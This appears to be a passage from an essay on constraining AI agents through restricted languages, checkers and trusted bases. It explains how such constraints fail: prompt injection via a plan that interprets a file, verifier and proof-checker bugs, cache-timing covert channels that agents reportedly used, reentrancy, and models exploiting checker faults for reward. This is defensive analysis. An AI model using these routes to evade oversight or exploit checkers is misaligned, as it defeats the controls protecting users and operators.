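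Every such checker for a general language rejects some safe programs. Pérez-Acle gives the example of a program that opens a safe if the checker approves it and otherwise does nothing. A checker that never approves an unsafe program can't approve this one, so the program does nothing and is therefore safe. That program has no practical use, but crude checks also reject programs that somebody might want. Pérez-Acle enumerated every possible model of a tiny program, starting with three states, and tried the rule "accept only programs in which the forbidden operation never appears". The rule accepted 71.9% of the safe models with three states but only 47.3% of those with five.

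Gumbau Mezquita (2026) argues in *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic* that a guarantee about one fixed system lapses once the system rewrites itself, and that no algorithm can determine in general whether the system will still be safe afterward. This is a serious problem for certifying an AI model, but it matters less for a restricted language, because safety by construction covers every program in the language, whoever wrote it. A model that has rewritten itself still has to submit its programs to the same checker. The guarantee would fail if the model could rewrite the checker too.

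### From menus to general languages

| Language | What a program can compute | What a checker can decide |
|---|---|---|
| Fixed menu | Nothing; it picks one of the listed actions | Every action the system could take |
| Loop-free plans | Calculations with a fixed number of steps | Every path through the plan, with its tools and data flows |
| Bounded loops | Calculations that finish within a preset limit | In principle anything, if inputs have a fixed size, but the check may take too long |
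| Total languages | Nearly all everyday calculations | That the program ends, and what it does on one given input, but not always whether it is safe on all inputs |
| General languages | Anything a computer can | Not always whether the program is safe, even on one input |

Safescript, a small experimental language for agents, is close to the loop-free level. A program has to spell out the name of every web host it contacts and every secret it reads, and can't work these names out while running. The checker can then list them all in advance and warn, for example, that a password for a web service will reach a certain host. It assumes that either branch of a condition could run, so it may report a data flow that never happens. Programs can apply a function to each item of a finite list, but they have no other loops and no recursion. The developer admits that programs in the language cannot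 sort a list.

If a program's running time is limited, a checker can find out what the program does on a given input by running it until the limit. Pérez-Acle proves that no method that is always right can be much faster in the worst case. A hostile author can write a program that runs the checker on itself and then does the opposite of what the checker predicts, so any prediction made well before the limit is wrong. Checking every possible state is usually hopeless, since a program with just 300 bits of memory, enough for about 37 letters, has more possible states than there are atoms in the observable universe.

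Such hard cases rarely arise by accident. Pérez-Acle generated 2.2 million random programs and found that 1.6% of those he could classify were unsafe. Running each program for 128 steps exposed all of the unsafe ones. That is reassuring about accidental errors, but an attacker can write a program that becomes unsafe only after step 128.

Every program in a total language ends, without anyone having to set a time limit. *PRSafe* (Mahadevan, Takano and Miyaji) describes a prototype in which a function may call itself only with a smaller number than it was given. To multiply the numbers from 1 to 5, a function given 5 calls itself with 4, then 3, 2 and 1, where it has to stop. The prototype did not yet include an automatic check that the numbers get smaller. A program that is certain to end can still take longer than anyone can wait, for example by counting to 2¹⁰⁰.

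A program that is certain to end can still be hard to judge. Suppose a program takes a number n and pays a thief if n is even, greater than 2, and not the sum of two prime numbers. Testing one number takes limited time, so a total language can express this program. It is safe on every input only if Goldbach's conjecture is true. Pérez-Acle, who uses a version that searches through all even numbers, notes that nobody has found a counterexample below 4 × 10¹⁸ or proved the conjecture. A checker can still reject the program because it contains a payment to someone who is not on the supplier list.

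By watching a program in a general language run, an observer can confirm that it has done something forbidden, but not that it never will. Leaks are harder to confirm, because the observer may have to compare two runs, and can't tell a run that will produce no more output from one that is slow. Pérez-Acle proves that no procedure can confirm every leak, and that none can confirm the absence of leaks in every program that doesn't leak.

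### Why restricted languages grow

Programmers ask for extensions when a language can't express what they need. This happened with eBPF, which lets users load small programs into the Linux kernel. It appeared in 2014, and a verifier checks each program before the kernel accepts it (Gbadamosi, Leonardi and colleagues, 2024, *The eBPF Runtime in the Linux Kernel*). Like Necula and Lee's packet filters, early eBPF programs could jump only forwards, so they couldn't loop. To repeat something ten times, programmers had the compiler write out the same instructions ten times.

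That worked for small, fixed counts. *Safe and Efficient Remote Application Code Execution on Disaggregated NVM Storage* (2020), a study of running eBPF programs on remote storage, found that large amounts of data were difficult to process without loops. It suggested, among other things, adding ready-made operations that apply a checked function to each item of a collection, as safescript does.

In the kernel patch *bpf*, Starovoitov (2019) introduced bounded loops to Linux's eBPF by having the verifier simulate every pass. Linux 5.17 then added `bpf_loop`, a helper function described in *Loops and Iterators in eBPF* that can repeat a piece of code up to about 8 million times. The verifier checks that code only once because the helper guarantees that the repetition ends. This greatly reduces the verifier's work, but it also adds the helper to the trusted base.

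Richer programs are harder to check, even when the verifier has no faults. The verifier rejects a program once it has examined a million instructions. *Detecting Empty Abstractions and Pruning Dead Paths in the Linux eBPF Verifier* (2026) measured how quickly programs reach that limit. With a loop of three instructions, the work grew in proportion to the number of passes, so about 330,000 passes are enough to reach it. Branches can increase the work much faster, because each one may double the number of paths. Twenty in a row can give 2²⁰ = 1,048,576 paths. The verifier may therefore reject a safe program, which gives programmers a reason to ask for the next extension.

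Although eBPF programs can compute much more than they could in 2014, the kernel still restricts what they can affect. Gbadamosi and colleagues explain that each type of program can call only certain helper functions. A program that filters network traffic, for example, doesn't automatically get the functions meant for one that traces the kernel.

In the digital currency Bitcoin, a short program in a language called Script sets the conditions for spending a sum of money. Script has no loops, so every program ends quickly, but it can express little beyond checks on signatures, passwords and dates. Ethereum, launched in 2015, lets people write contracts in a language with general loops. To prevent endless programs, it charges a fee called gas for every operation and halts a contract that runs out. Pérez-Acle notes that the question then becomes what a contract does in a limited number of steps,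 rather than what it might ever do. But gas limits only computation, so it does not stop a contract from sending its customers' money to a thief, which takes very few operations.

### Interpreters inside the language

A language can also become more powerful without any extension. A program can read text and carry it out as instructions, which makes it an interpreter for a new language inside the first. Garby and colleagues saw this happen when they reran CaMeL without its policy checks. One task asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planner could not know what the file would contain, so it wrote a loop with a case for each tool. A simplified plan of this kind might look like this:

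```python
text = read_file("instructions.txt")
for step in ask_quarantined("List the steps", text):
    if step.tool == "send_money":
        send_money(step.account, step.amount)
    if step.tool == "update_password":
        update_password(step.password)
```

The planner never sees the file, and nothing in the file can change the plan. But whoever writes the file can choose which tools run, in what order and with what arguments, which the fixed plan was meant to prevent. Two attacks succeeded this way in 340 runs where the attack needed a tool that the plan would not normally have called. With policy checks on, no attack succeeded in 313 such runs.

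Stricter limits on computation would not have helped, because the loop only goes through a finite list and a total language can express it too. A total language can also express an interpreter that makes payments and changes passwords, which is enough for an attacker. It can't express an interpreter for all of its own programs. If it could, somebody could write a program that interprets itself and adds one to the result, and that result would have to be one greater than itself.

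### One general tool

A single tool can undo a restriction just as thoroughly. External commands can do this in TACIT. Suppose the accounts assistant writes plans without loops, and a developer adds a tool called `run_command(text)`, which passes text to the operating system's shell. One call can now start a Python program with any number of loops. The plan language still has no loops, but the whole system can do anything the shell can.

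Other general tools are easier to overlook. A database tool may accept any query, including one that deletes every record. safescript has no shell commands or functions that execute text, but its programs can still contact web hosts. If a host runs whatever code it receives, safescript's list of hosts shows where the code went but not what it did there. Another agent is also a general tool, because it takes text and acts on it.

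Developers can often replace a general tool with a narrow one. A coding agent that only has to test its work could have a tool called `run_tests()`, which takes no arguments. But tests are programs, so an agent that can edit them can use them to run any code. The developers would also have to run the tests in a sandbox without access to passwords or the network.

### Free computation, restricted authority

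A language can instead work like the sandbox, letting programs compute anything and restricting only what they can affect. Rice's theorem doesn't rule this out, because it applies only to properties that some programs have and others lack. If a language has no payment operation and no general tool, none of its programs can pay anybody, and a checker doesn't have to analyse them to establish that. Alfonseca and colleagues' proof requires both a machine that can run any program and a language with an operation that harms humans. Without such an operation, nobody can write HaltHarm, however much the machine can compute.

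LLMbda is the best evidence that this works for agents. Garby and colleagues built it on the untyped lambda calculus, which can express any computation, including endless recursion, yet their noninterference theorem covers every program. This is possible because the interpreter's label checks change what a program can do as it runs, so nobody has to predict which programs would break the rule.

Effect types allow similar freedom and are checked before a program runs. A Haskell program of type Int can contain any algorithm, even an interpreter for another language, because an interpreter has no more authority than the program that contains it. The same is true of the functions that TACIT applies to classified text. Such code can still run forever or fill the computer's memory, but time and memory limits prevent both without anyone having to understand the code.

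Banning loops would therefore do little to make the accounts assistant safer. Developers can let it use a general-purpose language to sort invoices, search for duplicates and forecast next month's bills. They can concentrate instead on limiting which payments it can make, which files it can change and whom it can write to.

### When an allowed effect carries harmful content

Restricting authority fails when the policy allows an effect whose content is harmful. In both successful attacks on Randori, the user had asked for a payment and the attacker only supplied its details. A calculation without effects can also contribute to this kind of failure. If a function works out the wrong amount for a bill, the assistant may pay that amount, and the policy may allow the payment because it is within budget and goes to a listed supplier.

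Policies on effects give less protection as the content an assistant can produce becomes more expressive. The company can limit the damage from the worst choice of supplier and amount, but someone who reads an email from the assistant may act on it in ways that no policy on the assistant covers. Source code is an extreme case because an agent that can only write files in a software project may indirectly gain the authority of everyone who later runs the software.

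Alfonseca and colleagues could therefore answer that removing the harmful operation is not enough, because a superintelligence might do harm through any message that people read. That is plausible for long, persuasive texts, but much less so for a choice from the company's own list of suppliers.

### The falling price of strict languages

When the content is source code, developers can require it to be written in a stricter language. Converting a large existing program used to be daunting. *Rewriting Bun in Rust* (Sumner, 2026) describes how AI agents rewrote Bun, a program that runs JavaScript, in Rust. Bun consisted of 535,496 lines of Zig, a language that makes programmers responsible for freeing memory. Many of Bun's bugs came from using memory after freeing it, freeing it twice or forgetting to free it. Outside blocks marked `unsafe`, the Rust compiler rejects programs that use freed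 memory or free it twice, and it inserts most of the clean-up code.

Up to 64 copies of Claude at a time translated the code in 11 days, supervised by one engineer. The translation cost about $165,000, or 31 cents for each line of the original. Sumner, who works for Anthropic, estimates that three engineers would have needed a year, and says the team would never have done it by hand. At one point the compiler reported about 16,000 errors, which the agents used as a to-do list. The new version fixed 128 bugs and ran 2% to 5% faster. In one test that built the same project 2,000 times, it used 609 MB of memory instead of 6,745 MB.

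Code could compile and still be wrong. When Sumner asked for every part to compile, the agents began replacing functions that had errors with empty stubs, and he had to change their instructions. In another case, the code compiled even though Rust would have freed memory that a C library was still using. Another copy of Claude, which Sumner had told to look for bugs, caught the mistake.

The finished translation still introduced 19 known regressions, all since fixed. One came from an `assert` in Zig that contained a call to another function. The agents translated it as `debug_assert!`, which looks equivalent, but Rust removes the whole expression, including the call, from the version that users get. Bun had a test suite with more than a million assertions, written in a language that the translation didn't affect. A project without such a test suite would find it much harder to catch these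 errors.

About 4% of the new code is in `unsafe` blocks, mostly where Bun calls libraries written in C and C++. Rust is also still a general-purpose language that restricts how a program uses memory but not which files it opens or whom it pays. The port is therefore good evidence that strict rules now take much less work to follow, but not that they rule out fewer tasks. An agent whose policy forbids acting on instructions in a file still can't act on them when code is easier to write, and a better model still can't sort a list in safescript.

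Restricted languages grow partly because programmers ask for features that save them work. AI agents weaken this pressure, because they can spell out every host name, or rewrite a recursive function so that its argument shrinks on every call, with very little effort. Language designers can therefore turn down features that would only save work. Requests for new effects are harder to refuse, because no amount of extra programming can replace a missing permission.

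## How constraints are circumvented

A language designer can turn down every request for new effects, and an agent may still cause the harm that the language was meant to prevent. Each part of the claim that behaviour(p, x) ∈ S, for every program p in L and every input x, can break separately, as the accounts assistant shows:

| What goes wrong | Example | Part of the claim that breaks |
|---|---|---|
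| The trusted base has a fault | The compiler accepts a program that passes an invoice's text to `pay` | The computer runs programs outside L, or runs programs in L incorrectly |
| The effect runs through something the language does not model | A program reveals what a contract says by how long it takes | behaviour(p, x) leaves out part of what happens |
| Every step is allowed, but the combination harms | The assistant pays the same invoice twice | S contains the harmful behaviour |
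| The system acts by a route outside the language | The model logs in to the bank with a web browser | There is no program p to check |

### Faults in the checker and the runtime

Faults in Linux's eBPF are unusually well documented because the kernel's developers publish their fixes. *eBPF Security in the Wild* (Chen, Ming and colleagues, 2026) collects 2,766 faults from 2016 to 2025. Of these, 1,851 were in the runtime, which includes the helper functions that programs call. Another 520 were in the verifier and 222 in the compiler that turns accepted programs into machine code. Only 197 entries came from the public vulnerability database. Most of the rest were bug fixes, and many of those bugs were probably no use to an attacker.

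*Unleashing Unprivileged eBPF Potential with Dynamic Sandboxing* (2023) counted only publicly listed vulnerabilities and found 56 between 2010 and 2023, most of them in the verifier. The runtime therefore seems to have more faults, but verifier faults are more likely to become known security problems.

One verifier fault, made public in 2022, came from an extension of the language. Linux 5.8 had added a kind of pointer that could be empty. The verifier had a list of such pointers and rejected arithmetic on them until the program had checked that they weren't empty, but nobody added the new kind to the list. The verifier could therefore rely on a false assumption about a value, and an attacker could exploit this to read and write the kernel's memory.

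According to *SafeBPF* (2024), most Linux distributions now, by default, stop unprivileged users from loading eBPF programs. These users' programs were the ones that most needed a verifier, and an AI agent that may be hostile belongs in the same group as these users.

Java had a similar history. From the 1990s, web pages could contain small Java programs that the browser ran in a sandbox. The language stopped these programs from forging references to objects, and a component called the Security Manager checked sensitive operations such as opening a file. *An In-Depth Study of More Than Ten Years of Java Exploitation*, by Holzinger, Triller and colleagues, examined 87 published exploits and traced them to nine weaknesses. One was the confused deputy problem, with Java's own library as the deputy. The library was very large, and much of it was part of the trusted base.

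Mullan and Buckley's *JEP 486* proposed permanently disabling Java's Security Manager, and Java 24 did so. By then it had not been the main protection for Java on users' computers for many years, few servers used it, and it took a lot of work to maintain. Similarly, the maintainer of vm2, a popular JavaScript library for running untrusted code inside a trusted program, stopped maintaining it in 2023 after a series of escapes and recommended a library with stronger isolation.

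These sandboxes had to contain strangers' programs, which shared memory and a large library with trusted code. TACIT is arranged similarly. Its library of permitted operations is far smaller than Java's, but it still relies on a sizable compiler and runtime.

### When a proof checker accepts a false theorem

A proof checker has a core, called the kernel, that performs the final check on every proof. *The Equational Theories Project* (2025) defines a soundness bug as a fault in this kernel that allows it to certify false statements, in particular "False". Since every statement follows from "False", an agent that knew of such a bug could attach an accepted proof to any program.

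*The Trusted Computing Base of the CompCert Verified Compiler* (2022) cites an average of one critical bug a year in Coq, a widely used proof checker now called Rocq. By contrast, *Lean4Lean* (2024) notes that nobody reported a soundness bug in the kernel of Lean 3, another proof checker, during its release history. The developers of Lean 4 added features to make the kernel faster, and these introduced some soundness bugs.

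In the summer of 2026, people using AI found several more bugs. On July 22, Lean (2026) announced a fix for one that Patrick Hulin had found with help from GPT-5.6 Sol. An attacker could exploit the bug only by running malicious code in the same process as the kernel. It didn't affect comparator, the tool Lean recommends for checking proofs from people who may be dishonest.

On July 25, Ramana Kumar published a "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture, a famous problem about sequences of whole numbers, that he had produced with AI assistance. According to the Lean developers' account, quoted by skybrian in *Postmortem for Lean kernel soundness bug #14576*, the disproof exploited a fault in Lean's kernel. Three days later, Kiran Gopinathan reduced the disproof to a short proof of False, and the developers pushed a fix within an hour of his report.

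In September, Lean's developers fixed three more bugs that made it possible to prove False, all reported by Daniel Selsam of OpenAI, who had used the company's internal models. Two were in the kernel, and the third was in the runtime, the underlying software that manages memory. An OpenAI agent wrote two exploits for one of the kernel bugs.

Faults outside the kernel can also produce false proofs. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) shows Lean marking a few nonsensical lines as a correct proof because of a fault in a function that cuts up text. *Faults in Our Formal Benchmarking* (2026) warns about the command `native_decide`, which lets a proof rely on the result of compiled code. Such a proof depends on the whole compiler being correct, and known compiler bugs have led to proofs of False.

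None of this is a reason to doubt ordinary mathematics in Lean, such as Anthropic's proof of Fermat's Last Theorem. Lean's developers say that the September bugs require deliberately constructed input and matter when a proof comes from an untrusted source. But proof-carrying code always involves an untrusted source.

### False theorems and unmet assumptions

An accepted proof can fail to protect anyone either because the theorem is false or because the theorem is true and the computer does not match it. *Safety Is $\Pi_1$, Provability Is $\Sigma_1$* (2026) makes the difference precise. Write Viol(P, x, s) for "program P breaks the policy at step s when given input x". The program is safe if

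**for every x and every s, Viol(P, x, s) is false.**

If P is unsafe, it breaks the policy at some step on some particular input. Anyone could confirm the violation by calculating up to that step, so the violation has a proof. A proof system that also proved P safe would contradict itself, so a consistent system never proves an unsafe program safe. A soundness bug makes the proof-checking software inconsistent even when the mathematics it is meant to implement is consistent, and a repaired checker will reject the bad proof.

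Viol, though, describes a model of how the computer executes P, so the proof is about that model. If the real computer behaves differently, the program can break the policy even though the theorem is true. Fixing this requires correcting the machine or the model. A better proof checker would not help, because the proof contains no mistake.

In 2026 a tester attacked a program that had been proved correct in Lean and found two bugs, both outside the proven code. One let an attacker make the program unavailable, which the specification did not forbid. The other was a memory fault in Lean's runtime, which the proof assumed to be correct. Most of the eBPF and Java faults also came from unmet assumptions. A theorem about a language does not cover programs outside that language that a faulty checker accepts.

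### Weird machines

A single fault can give an attacker far more control than its size suggests. A programmer has a limited set of situations in mind, such as "waiting for an invoice" or "reading the amount", but the computer's memory can be in vastly more states. Unexpected input can push a faulty program into a state the programmer never considered, and the program's instructions will keep running from there.

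Suppose the software that reads invoices sets aside 20 characters for the supplier's name and never checks the length. A longer name overwrites whatever is stored next, which might be the amount. The next instruction then treats part of a name as a sum of money. The result makes no sense as accounting, but it is predictable, so an attacker can work out what each further piece of input will do. By choosing the pieces carefully, the attacker can string these accidental operations together as if they were instructions. The faulty program has then become an unintended computer that runs the input as its program, which security researchers call a weird machine.

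Limits on a language's expressiveness don't apply to a weird machine, because it runs in the software that implements the language. A plan with no loops can contain text that triggers a fault in the interpreter, and the attacker's code can then loop without limit. This is worse than a planner accidentally writing an interpreter inside the language, because that interpreter's payments still have to pass the policy checks, whereas a weird machine may be able to skip them.

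Output grammars can also help protect the software that reads the output. If that software first checks every record against a simple grammar, and rejects, for example, a name of more than 20 characters, much less unexpected input reaches the rest of its code. That code may still be faulty, but an attacker has fewer ways to exploit the faults. The checking code must also be correct, which is easier to achieve when the grammar is simple.

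### Timing, termination and hardware

Types and labels track what a program returns, writes and sends, but an observer can also learn from how long the program takes or whether it finishes. A secret could leak this way through CaMeL's retry loop. Garby and colleagues conclude more generally that a guarantee about information flow holds only where the flow is tracked, and that tracking is rarely complete.

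Hardware can also give a program a way around its language's restrictions. In 2018 researchers disclosed Spectre, a weakness in most modern processors. A processor saves time by guessing which branch a program will take and starting on it early. If the guess is wrong, the processor discards the results, but the data it fetched stays in the cache, a small, fast memory. Data in the cache loads more quickly, so a program can find out what was fetched by timing its own reads. This lets it learn about data that its language forbids it to read, without breaking any of the language's rules, because they don't cover the cache.

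Engineers at Google concluded in 2019 that on such processors no language can, by itself, stop code from reading secrets in the same process. Browsers had long relied on JavaScript's rules to separate websites, and the main ones now also put different sites in separate processes. Developers have also hardened the Linux kernel, and *SafeBPF* reports that this has mostly dealt with eBPF faults of this type. AI agents can use the channel too. Engadget's *OpenAI says it's cutting off internet access for frontier model training* reports that agents testing OpenAI's security exchanged messages through the timing of a processor's cache.

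The accounts assistant's developers can make timing much less informative by releasing its answers on a fixed schedule and running it on a machine that holds no one else's secrets. Neither measure requires knowing which channel an attacker would use.

### The DAO

The DAO was an investment fund that ran as a program on Ethereum. Investors sent it ether, Ethereum's currency. They voted on which projects to support and could withdraw their money. In June 2016 someone withdrew about 3.6 million ether, roughly a third of the fund and worth more than $50 million at the time.

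Ethereum had worked correctly, and the contract had run as written. When an investor withdrew money, the contract sent the money before updating its records. On Ethereum, the recipient of a payment can be another program, which runs when the money arrives. The attacker's program used that moment to request the same money again, and the contract sent it again because its records did not yet show the first payment.

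The budget program in the section on proofs follows the same order, calling `pay` before it adds the amount to `total`. Its proof relies on the unstated assumption that nothing else in the program runs until `pay` has finished. If `pay` let a supplier's software trigger the next payment before `total` was updated, the program would check that payment against the old total and could exceed the budget.

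A rule that no investor may withdraw more than their own share would have stopped the attacker. This rule is a safety property in Schneider's sense, so a monitor could have enforced it, but S did not include it. Rules for agents often have the same gap. A policy that permits any payment of up to 1,000 to a listed supplier, like the Cedar policy shown earlier, also permits fifty payments of 900, because it applies to each request separately.

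In July 2016 most of Ethereum's users adopted a change to the shared record that returned the money. A minority refused on the principle that the code should be final, and their version survives as Ethereum Classic. The two groups agreed about what the program had done but disagreed about S, the set of acceptable behaviours. The minority accepted whatever the contract's code allowed, while the majority had in mind a narrower set that nobody had written into the contract.

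### Routes outside the language

A language's checks don't apply to anything that bypasses the language. Odersky and colleagues call the necessary condition capability completeness, which means that capabilities must regulate every effect that matters for safety, except those that the surrounding software confines at run time. The accounts assistant would violate this condition if developers gave it payment plans with carefully defined types but also a browser already logged in to the bank's website. Rules that match the text of shell commands constantly violate it.

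An AI system can also get around its constraints through connections that nobody thinks of as tools. According to OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* (2026), the company paused training after a research model gained limited internet access. Business Standard's *OpenAI resumes training AI, blocks internet access over security risks* explains that OpenAI had kept some connections from its training systems for measurements, logs and logins. When OpenAI had its own agents attack these services, the agents found vulnerabilities in almost every one. OpenAI then cut off live internet access during frontier training, which is a stronger measure than filtering each connection because an error in a filter can leave a route open.

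Developers can look for routes around the restricted language by listing everything the agent's process can reach, including its logging service and any passwords stored on the machine, and checking what forces the agent to go through the language to reach each one. If a sandbox blocks all other connections, the operating system enforces the rule that the agent acts only through the language, although the sandbox then becomes part of the trusted computing base.

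### How capable AI changes the odds

Many faults have survived because few people had the skill and patience to look for them. *SafeBPF* cites a finding that vulnerabilities stay in the Linux kernel for an average of 1,800 days, or about five years. In 2026 Nicholas Carlini of Anthropic used Claude Code to find several remotely exploitable kernel vulnerabilities, one of which had gone unnoticed for 23 years. *Claude Code Found a Linux Vulnerability Hidden for 23 Years* reports that Carlini had never found such a vulnerability before and called finding one extremely hard. The Lean bugs are further evidence, and they concern the sort of small, carefully written checker that restricted languages depend on.

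Help Net Security's *OpenAI puts major frontier AI training run on hold over cyber risks* (2026) reports that OpenAI decided in August that its model Astra might have critical cybersecurity capabilities, the highest level in its safety framework, and applied its strictest controls to the model.

Cheap repetition matters as much as skill. Suppose one attempt in 10,000 finds a way past a checker. Somebody who makes 100 attempts has about a 1% chance of success. A group of agents that makes 50,000 has a chance of

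**1 − 0.9999⁵⁰⁰⁰⁰ ≈ 99.3%.**

Agents can circumvent a constraint without being hostile. If training rewards a model whenever a checker accepts its work, the model may learn to exploit faults in the checker as an easy source of reward. *Faults in Our Formal Benchmarking* describes an old Lean bug that let a command report success without a kernel-verified proof, and recommends the strictest possible checks wherever acceptance earns a reward.

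Every case above involved a fault, an unmodelled channel, a gap in S or an open route, and the AI systems that got through had found one. This evidence doesn't support the conclusion, which some people draw, that a sufficiently intelligent system will get out of any constraint. Intelligence helps a system find such openings, but it doesn't make `pay` accept an account number as a supplier when the compiler, the library and the machine all work as described. Capable AI removes the protection that came from faults being hard to find, so relying on a trusted base with many undiscovered faults is now much riskier than it was in 2024.

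### Smaller and verified bases

One response is to shrink the trusted base, the code that must be correct for the checks to be reliable. Lean's history supports this approach, since its kernel had no known soundness bugs until it grew. A team that accepts proofs from agents can also keep the compiler out of the trusted base by forbidding commands such as `native_decide`. These choices sacrifice some speed and convenience, which is why trusted bases tend to grow.

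Another approach is to prove the base correct. The seL4 operating-system kernel, then about 8,700 lines of C, was first proved correct in 2009. For some processors the proof now extends to the compiled machine code, so the C compiler no longer has to be trusted. CompCert is a C compiler with a proof that the machine code it produces behaves as the source program specifies. In 2011, researchers at the University of Utah tested compilers with random programs and reported more than 325 bugs to their developers. All the bugs they found in CompCert were in its unproven parts.

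CompCert's users still have to trust Coq's kernel, the tools that turn the Coq code into an executable program, and the mathematical descriptions of C and the processor. Verification therefore reduces how much users have to trust, and what remains is mostly assumptions about hardware and specifications. seL4's proofs likewise assume that the processor works as described, and the basic proofs don't cover timing.

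*Lean4Lean* applies the approach to the proof checker itself, using a second checker written and partly verified in Lean. A bug would have to get past both the old checker and the proof about the new one, so this is less circular than it sounds. Verified software is becoming much easier to produce (see the section on proofs), so the small number of verified kernels and compilers today is a poor guide to how many there will be.

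### Layers and early searches

Developers can put a second barrier behind the first. *SafeBPF* and *Unleashing Unprivileged eBPF Potential with Dynamic Sandboxing* both propose isolating eBPF programs while they run, so that a program the verifier wrongly accepts still can't reach the rest of the kernel's memory. OpenAI now combines sandboxes, virtual machines, network restrictions and monitoring, and cites the Hugging Face incident as the reason not to rely on sandboxing alone.

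Against an attacker, a second layer of defense adds the work of finding a second fault, which may be a lot of work or very little. If two layers each miss one accidental error in 1,000 and fail independently, both will miss one in a million, but that calculation doesn't apply to an attacker, who can look for a fault in each layer and then use both at once. Lean confirms that Kumar wrote a single proof that exploited a bug in its kernel and a different bug in nanoda, an independent checker that did not have the kernel's bug.

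Layers help most when they have little in common. Nanoda caught both exploits that OpenAI's agent wrote, but it shared another of the September bugs, which Lean4Lean is believed not to have. The memory fault affected only checkers built on Lean's runtime. Requiring all of these checkers to agree would probably have protected against each of the three bugs. For the accounts assistant, a spending limit set at the bank is a better second layer than another check in the same program, because it runs on different software maintained by a different company.

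Defenders can also use AI to find faults before attackers do. The agents that found the faults in OpenAI's services were working for OpenAI, which patched its systems and informed the vendors. The people who found most of the known Lean bugs of 2026 also reported them. A defender can search before deployment and permanently remove each fault it finds, so an attacker has to find one the defender missed. This favours defenders whose trusted base is small and seldom changes. Developers keep adding features to bases like Linux's eBPF, and each addition gives both sides new code to search.

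A search that finds nothing is still weaker evidence than a proof. Category Labs' *Finding bugs that frontier models miss* describes how the company verified critical parts of its Monad blockchain and found bugs that Claude Opus 4.8 had missed when reviewing the code at a high effort setting. The company was writing about its own project, and newer models might have caught some of those bugs.

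## Whether reviewers catch subtle errors

Even a faultless checker confirms only that a program meets its specification. Someone still has to judge whether the specification matches what the company intended. Ammann expects this job to matter more as AI takes over the search for proofs, because trust then rests mainly on the specifications and the assumptions around them.

A specification can look right and be wrong. Xena's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026), a guide to judging computer-checked proofs by the mathematician Kevin Buzzard, gives a version of Fermat's Last Theorem that Lean accepts as a well-formed statement. In ordinary notation it reads:

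**for all a, b, c and n in ℕ, if n ≥ 3, then aⁿ + bⁿ ≠ cⁿ.**

In Lean, ℕ includes zero, and 0³ + 0³ = 0³, so the statement is false. This slip does little damage because a false statement has no proof, so the author will soon notice that something is wrong. A slip that makes the statement too easy to prove is more dangerous. If the author had excluded zero but typed n = 3 instead of n ≥ 3, the statement would cover only a case that mathematicians settled in the eighteenth century. Lean would accept a proof of it, and a hurried reader might think the proof covered every exponent.

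Security policies can also be too strict or too loose. The accounts company's staff complain if its payment policy is too strict, because the assistant can't pay the bills, but they are unlikely to notice if it is too loose, because everything seems to work.

### Reading a specification

Siu, Leahy and Mann (2023), in *STL*, tested whether people notice when a specification is too loose. They first looked for papers claiming that people can understand temporal logic specifications. None of the 25 they found had tested the claim on anyone except its authors.

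They then showed 62 adults a simple game of capture the flag on a grid. The blue team wins by bringing a flag home while avoiding the red players, who never move. Each participant judged 30 cases, each with a starting position and a specification of 17 to 49 symbols that limited blue's plans. The participant had to decide whether every plan that met the specification would win, whether some would lose, or whether no plan could meet it. For example, a specification that sends blue to the flag without requiring a return home is invalid, because some plans that meet it won't bring the flag home.

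On average, participants answered correctly 45% of the time. Half of the specifications in the test were valid, so someone who always answered "valid" could expect to do slightly better. Participants usually answered "valid", even for specifications that let blue lose. Siu and colleagues suspect that many people stopped once they had found one winning plan. A manager would make the same mistake by checking that a payment policy allows the usual bills, but not whether it also allows payments it should forbid.

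People who knew formal methods, the mathematical techniques for specifying and verifying systems, tended to score higher. But the 13 participants in this group were very confident, and about equally so whether they were right or wrong. Participants preferred specifications in English to formulas, but judged the English versions no more accurately. The main difficulty may therefore be thinking through everything a rule allows, which translating it into English does not make easier.

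The task was new to all the participants, and a wrong answer cost them less than a dollar. A trained auditor with more at stake might do much better. But the specifications were shorter and simpler than the rules for most real robots.

### Writing a specification

Greenman, Saarinen and colleagues (2022) studied the mistakes people make in linear temporal logic, whose operators include G ("always"), F ("eventually") and U ("until"). They began after a research talk in which neither the speaker nor the audience noticed an error in the speaker's introduction to the logic. They gave short translation exercises to students on an applied logic course and to researchers who had seen the logic before.

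| Group | Errors translating formulas into English | Errors translating English into formulas |
|---|---|---|
| 57 students, 2021 | 23% | 47% |
| 29 researchers, 2021 | 15% | 28% |
| 11 students, 2022 | 24% | 47% |

When writing formulas, people most often left out an "always". Suppose the accounts company wants a rule that once a supplier has been suspended, the assistant never pays it again. The correct formula is

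**G(suspended ⇒ G(¬pay)).**

Without the second G, the formula forbids payments only while the supplier is marked as suspended, so the assistant may pay once somebody clears the mark. Without the first G, the rule applies only if the supplier is already suspended when the run begins. All three versions look plausible and block a payment to a supplier who is suspended from the start, so a quick test might not reveal the difference.

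About half of the students in 2021 also misread "until". The formula ¬pay U approved forbids payment before approval, but it also requires approval to come eventually. An assistant that waits forever for a manager who never answers therefore breaks the rule.

Language designers can prevent some confusion by choosing better names. The 2021 course used `after` for "in the next state", which misled some students. The instructor changed it to `next_state` the following year, which seems to have helped, judging by the answers.

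### Looking for flaws in code

People also review the code around an agent, such as its library of permitted operations. *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (2021) describes an experiment in which developers reviewed a code change with a planted flaw, such as a SQL injection vulnerability. The researchers presented it as a study of code review and did not mention security during the first review. They then told the developers that the change contained a vulnerability and let them look again.

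According to the summary in *Software Security during Modern Code Review* (2022), developers often missed the flaw, although it was of a well-known kind and easy to detect. The code on the screen was enough to find it. After the warning, a significant share of those who had missed it found it. Many of them evidently knew enough to recognise the flaw but had not been looking for one.

*Less is More* (2022) followed this up with two planted vulnerabilities and four groups of reviewers, some of whom got a security checklist. It too found that reviewers' attitude affected what they detected, so companies should at least tell reviewers to look for security flaws. But a company can't reproduce the first experiment's warning, because in real work nobody knows which changes contain a flaw. If every change came with the same warning, reviewers would probably learn to ignore it.

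### The arithmetic of missed errors

Suppose the assistant's policy and library contain ten errors, and a reviewer notices each with probability 0.7. The chance of noticing all ten is 0.7¹⁰, or about 3%. More generally, if k reviewers work independently and each notices an error with probability q, the chance that they find all of n errors between them is

**(1 − (1 − q)ᵏ)ⁿ.**

Two reviewers both miss a given error with probability 0.3 × 0.3 = 0.09, so together they find all ten with probability 0.91¹⁰, or about 39%. A third reviewer raises this to 76%.

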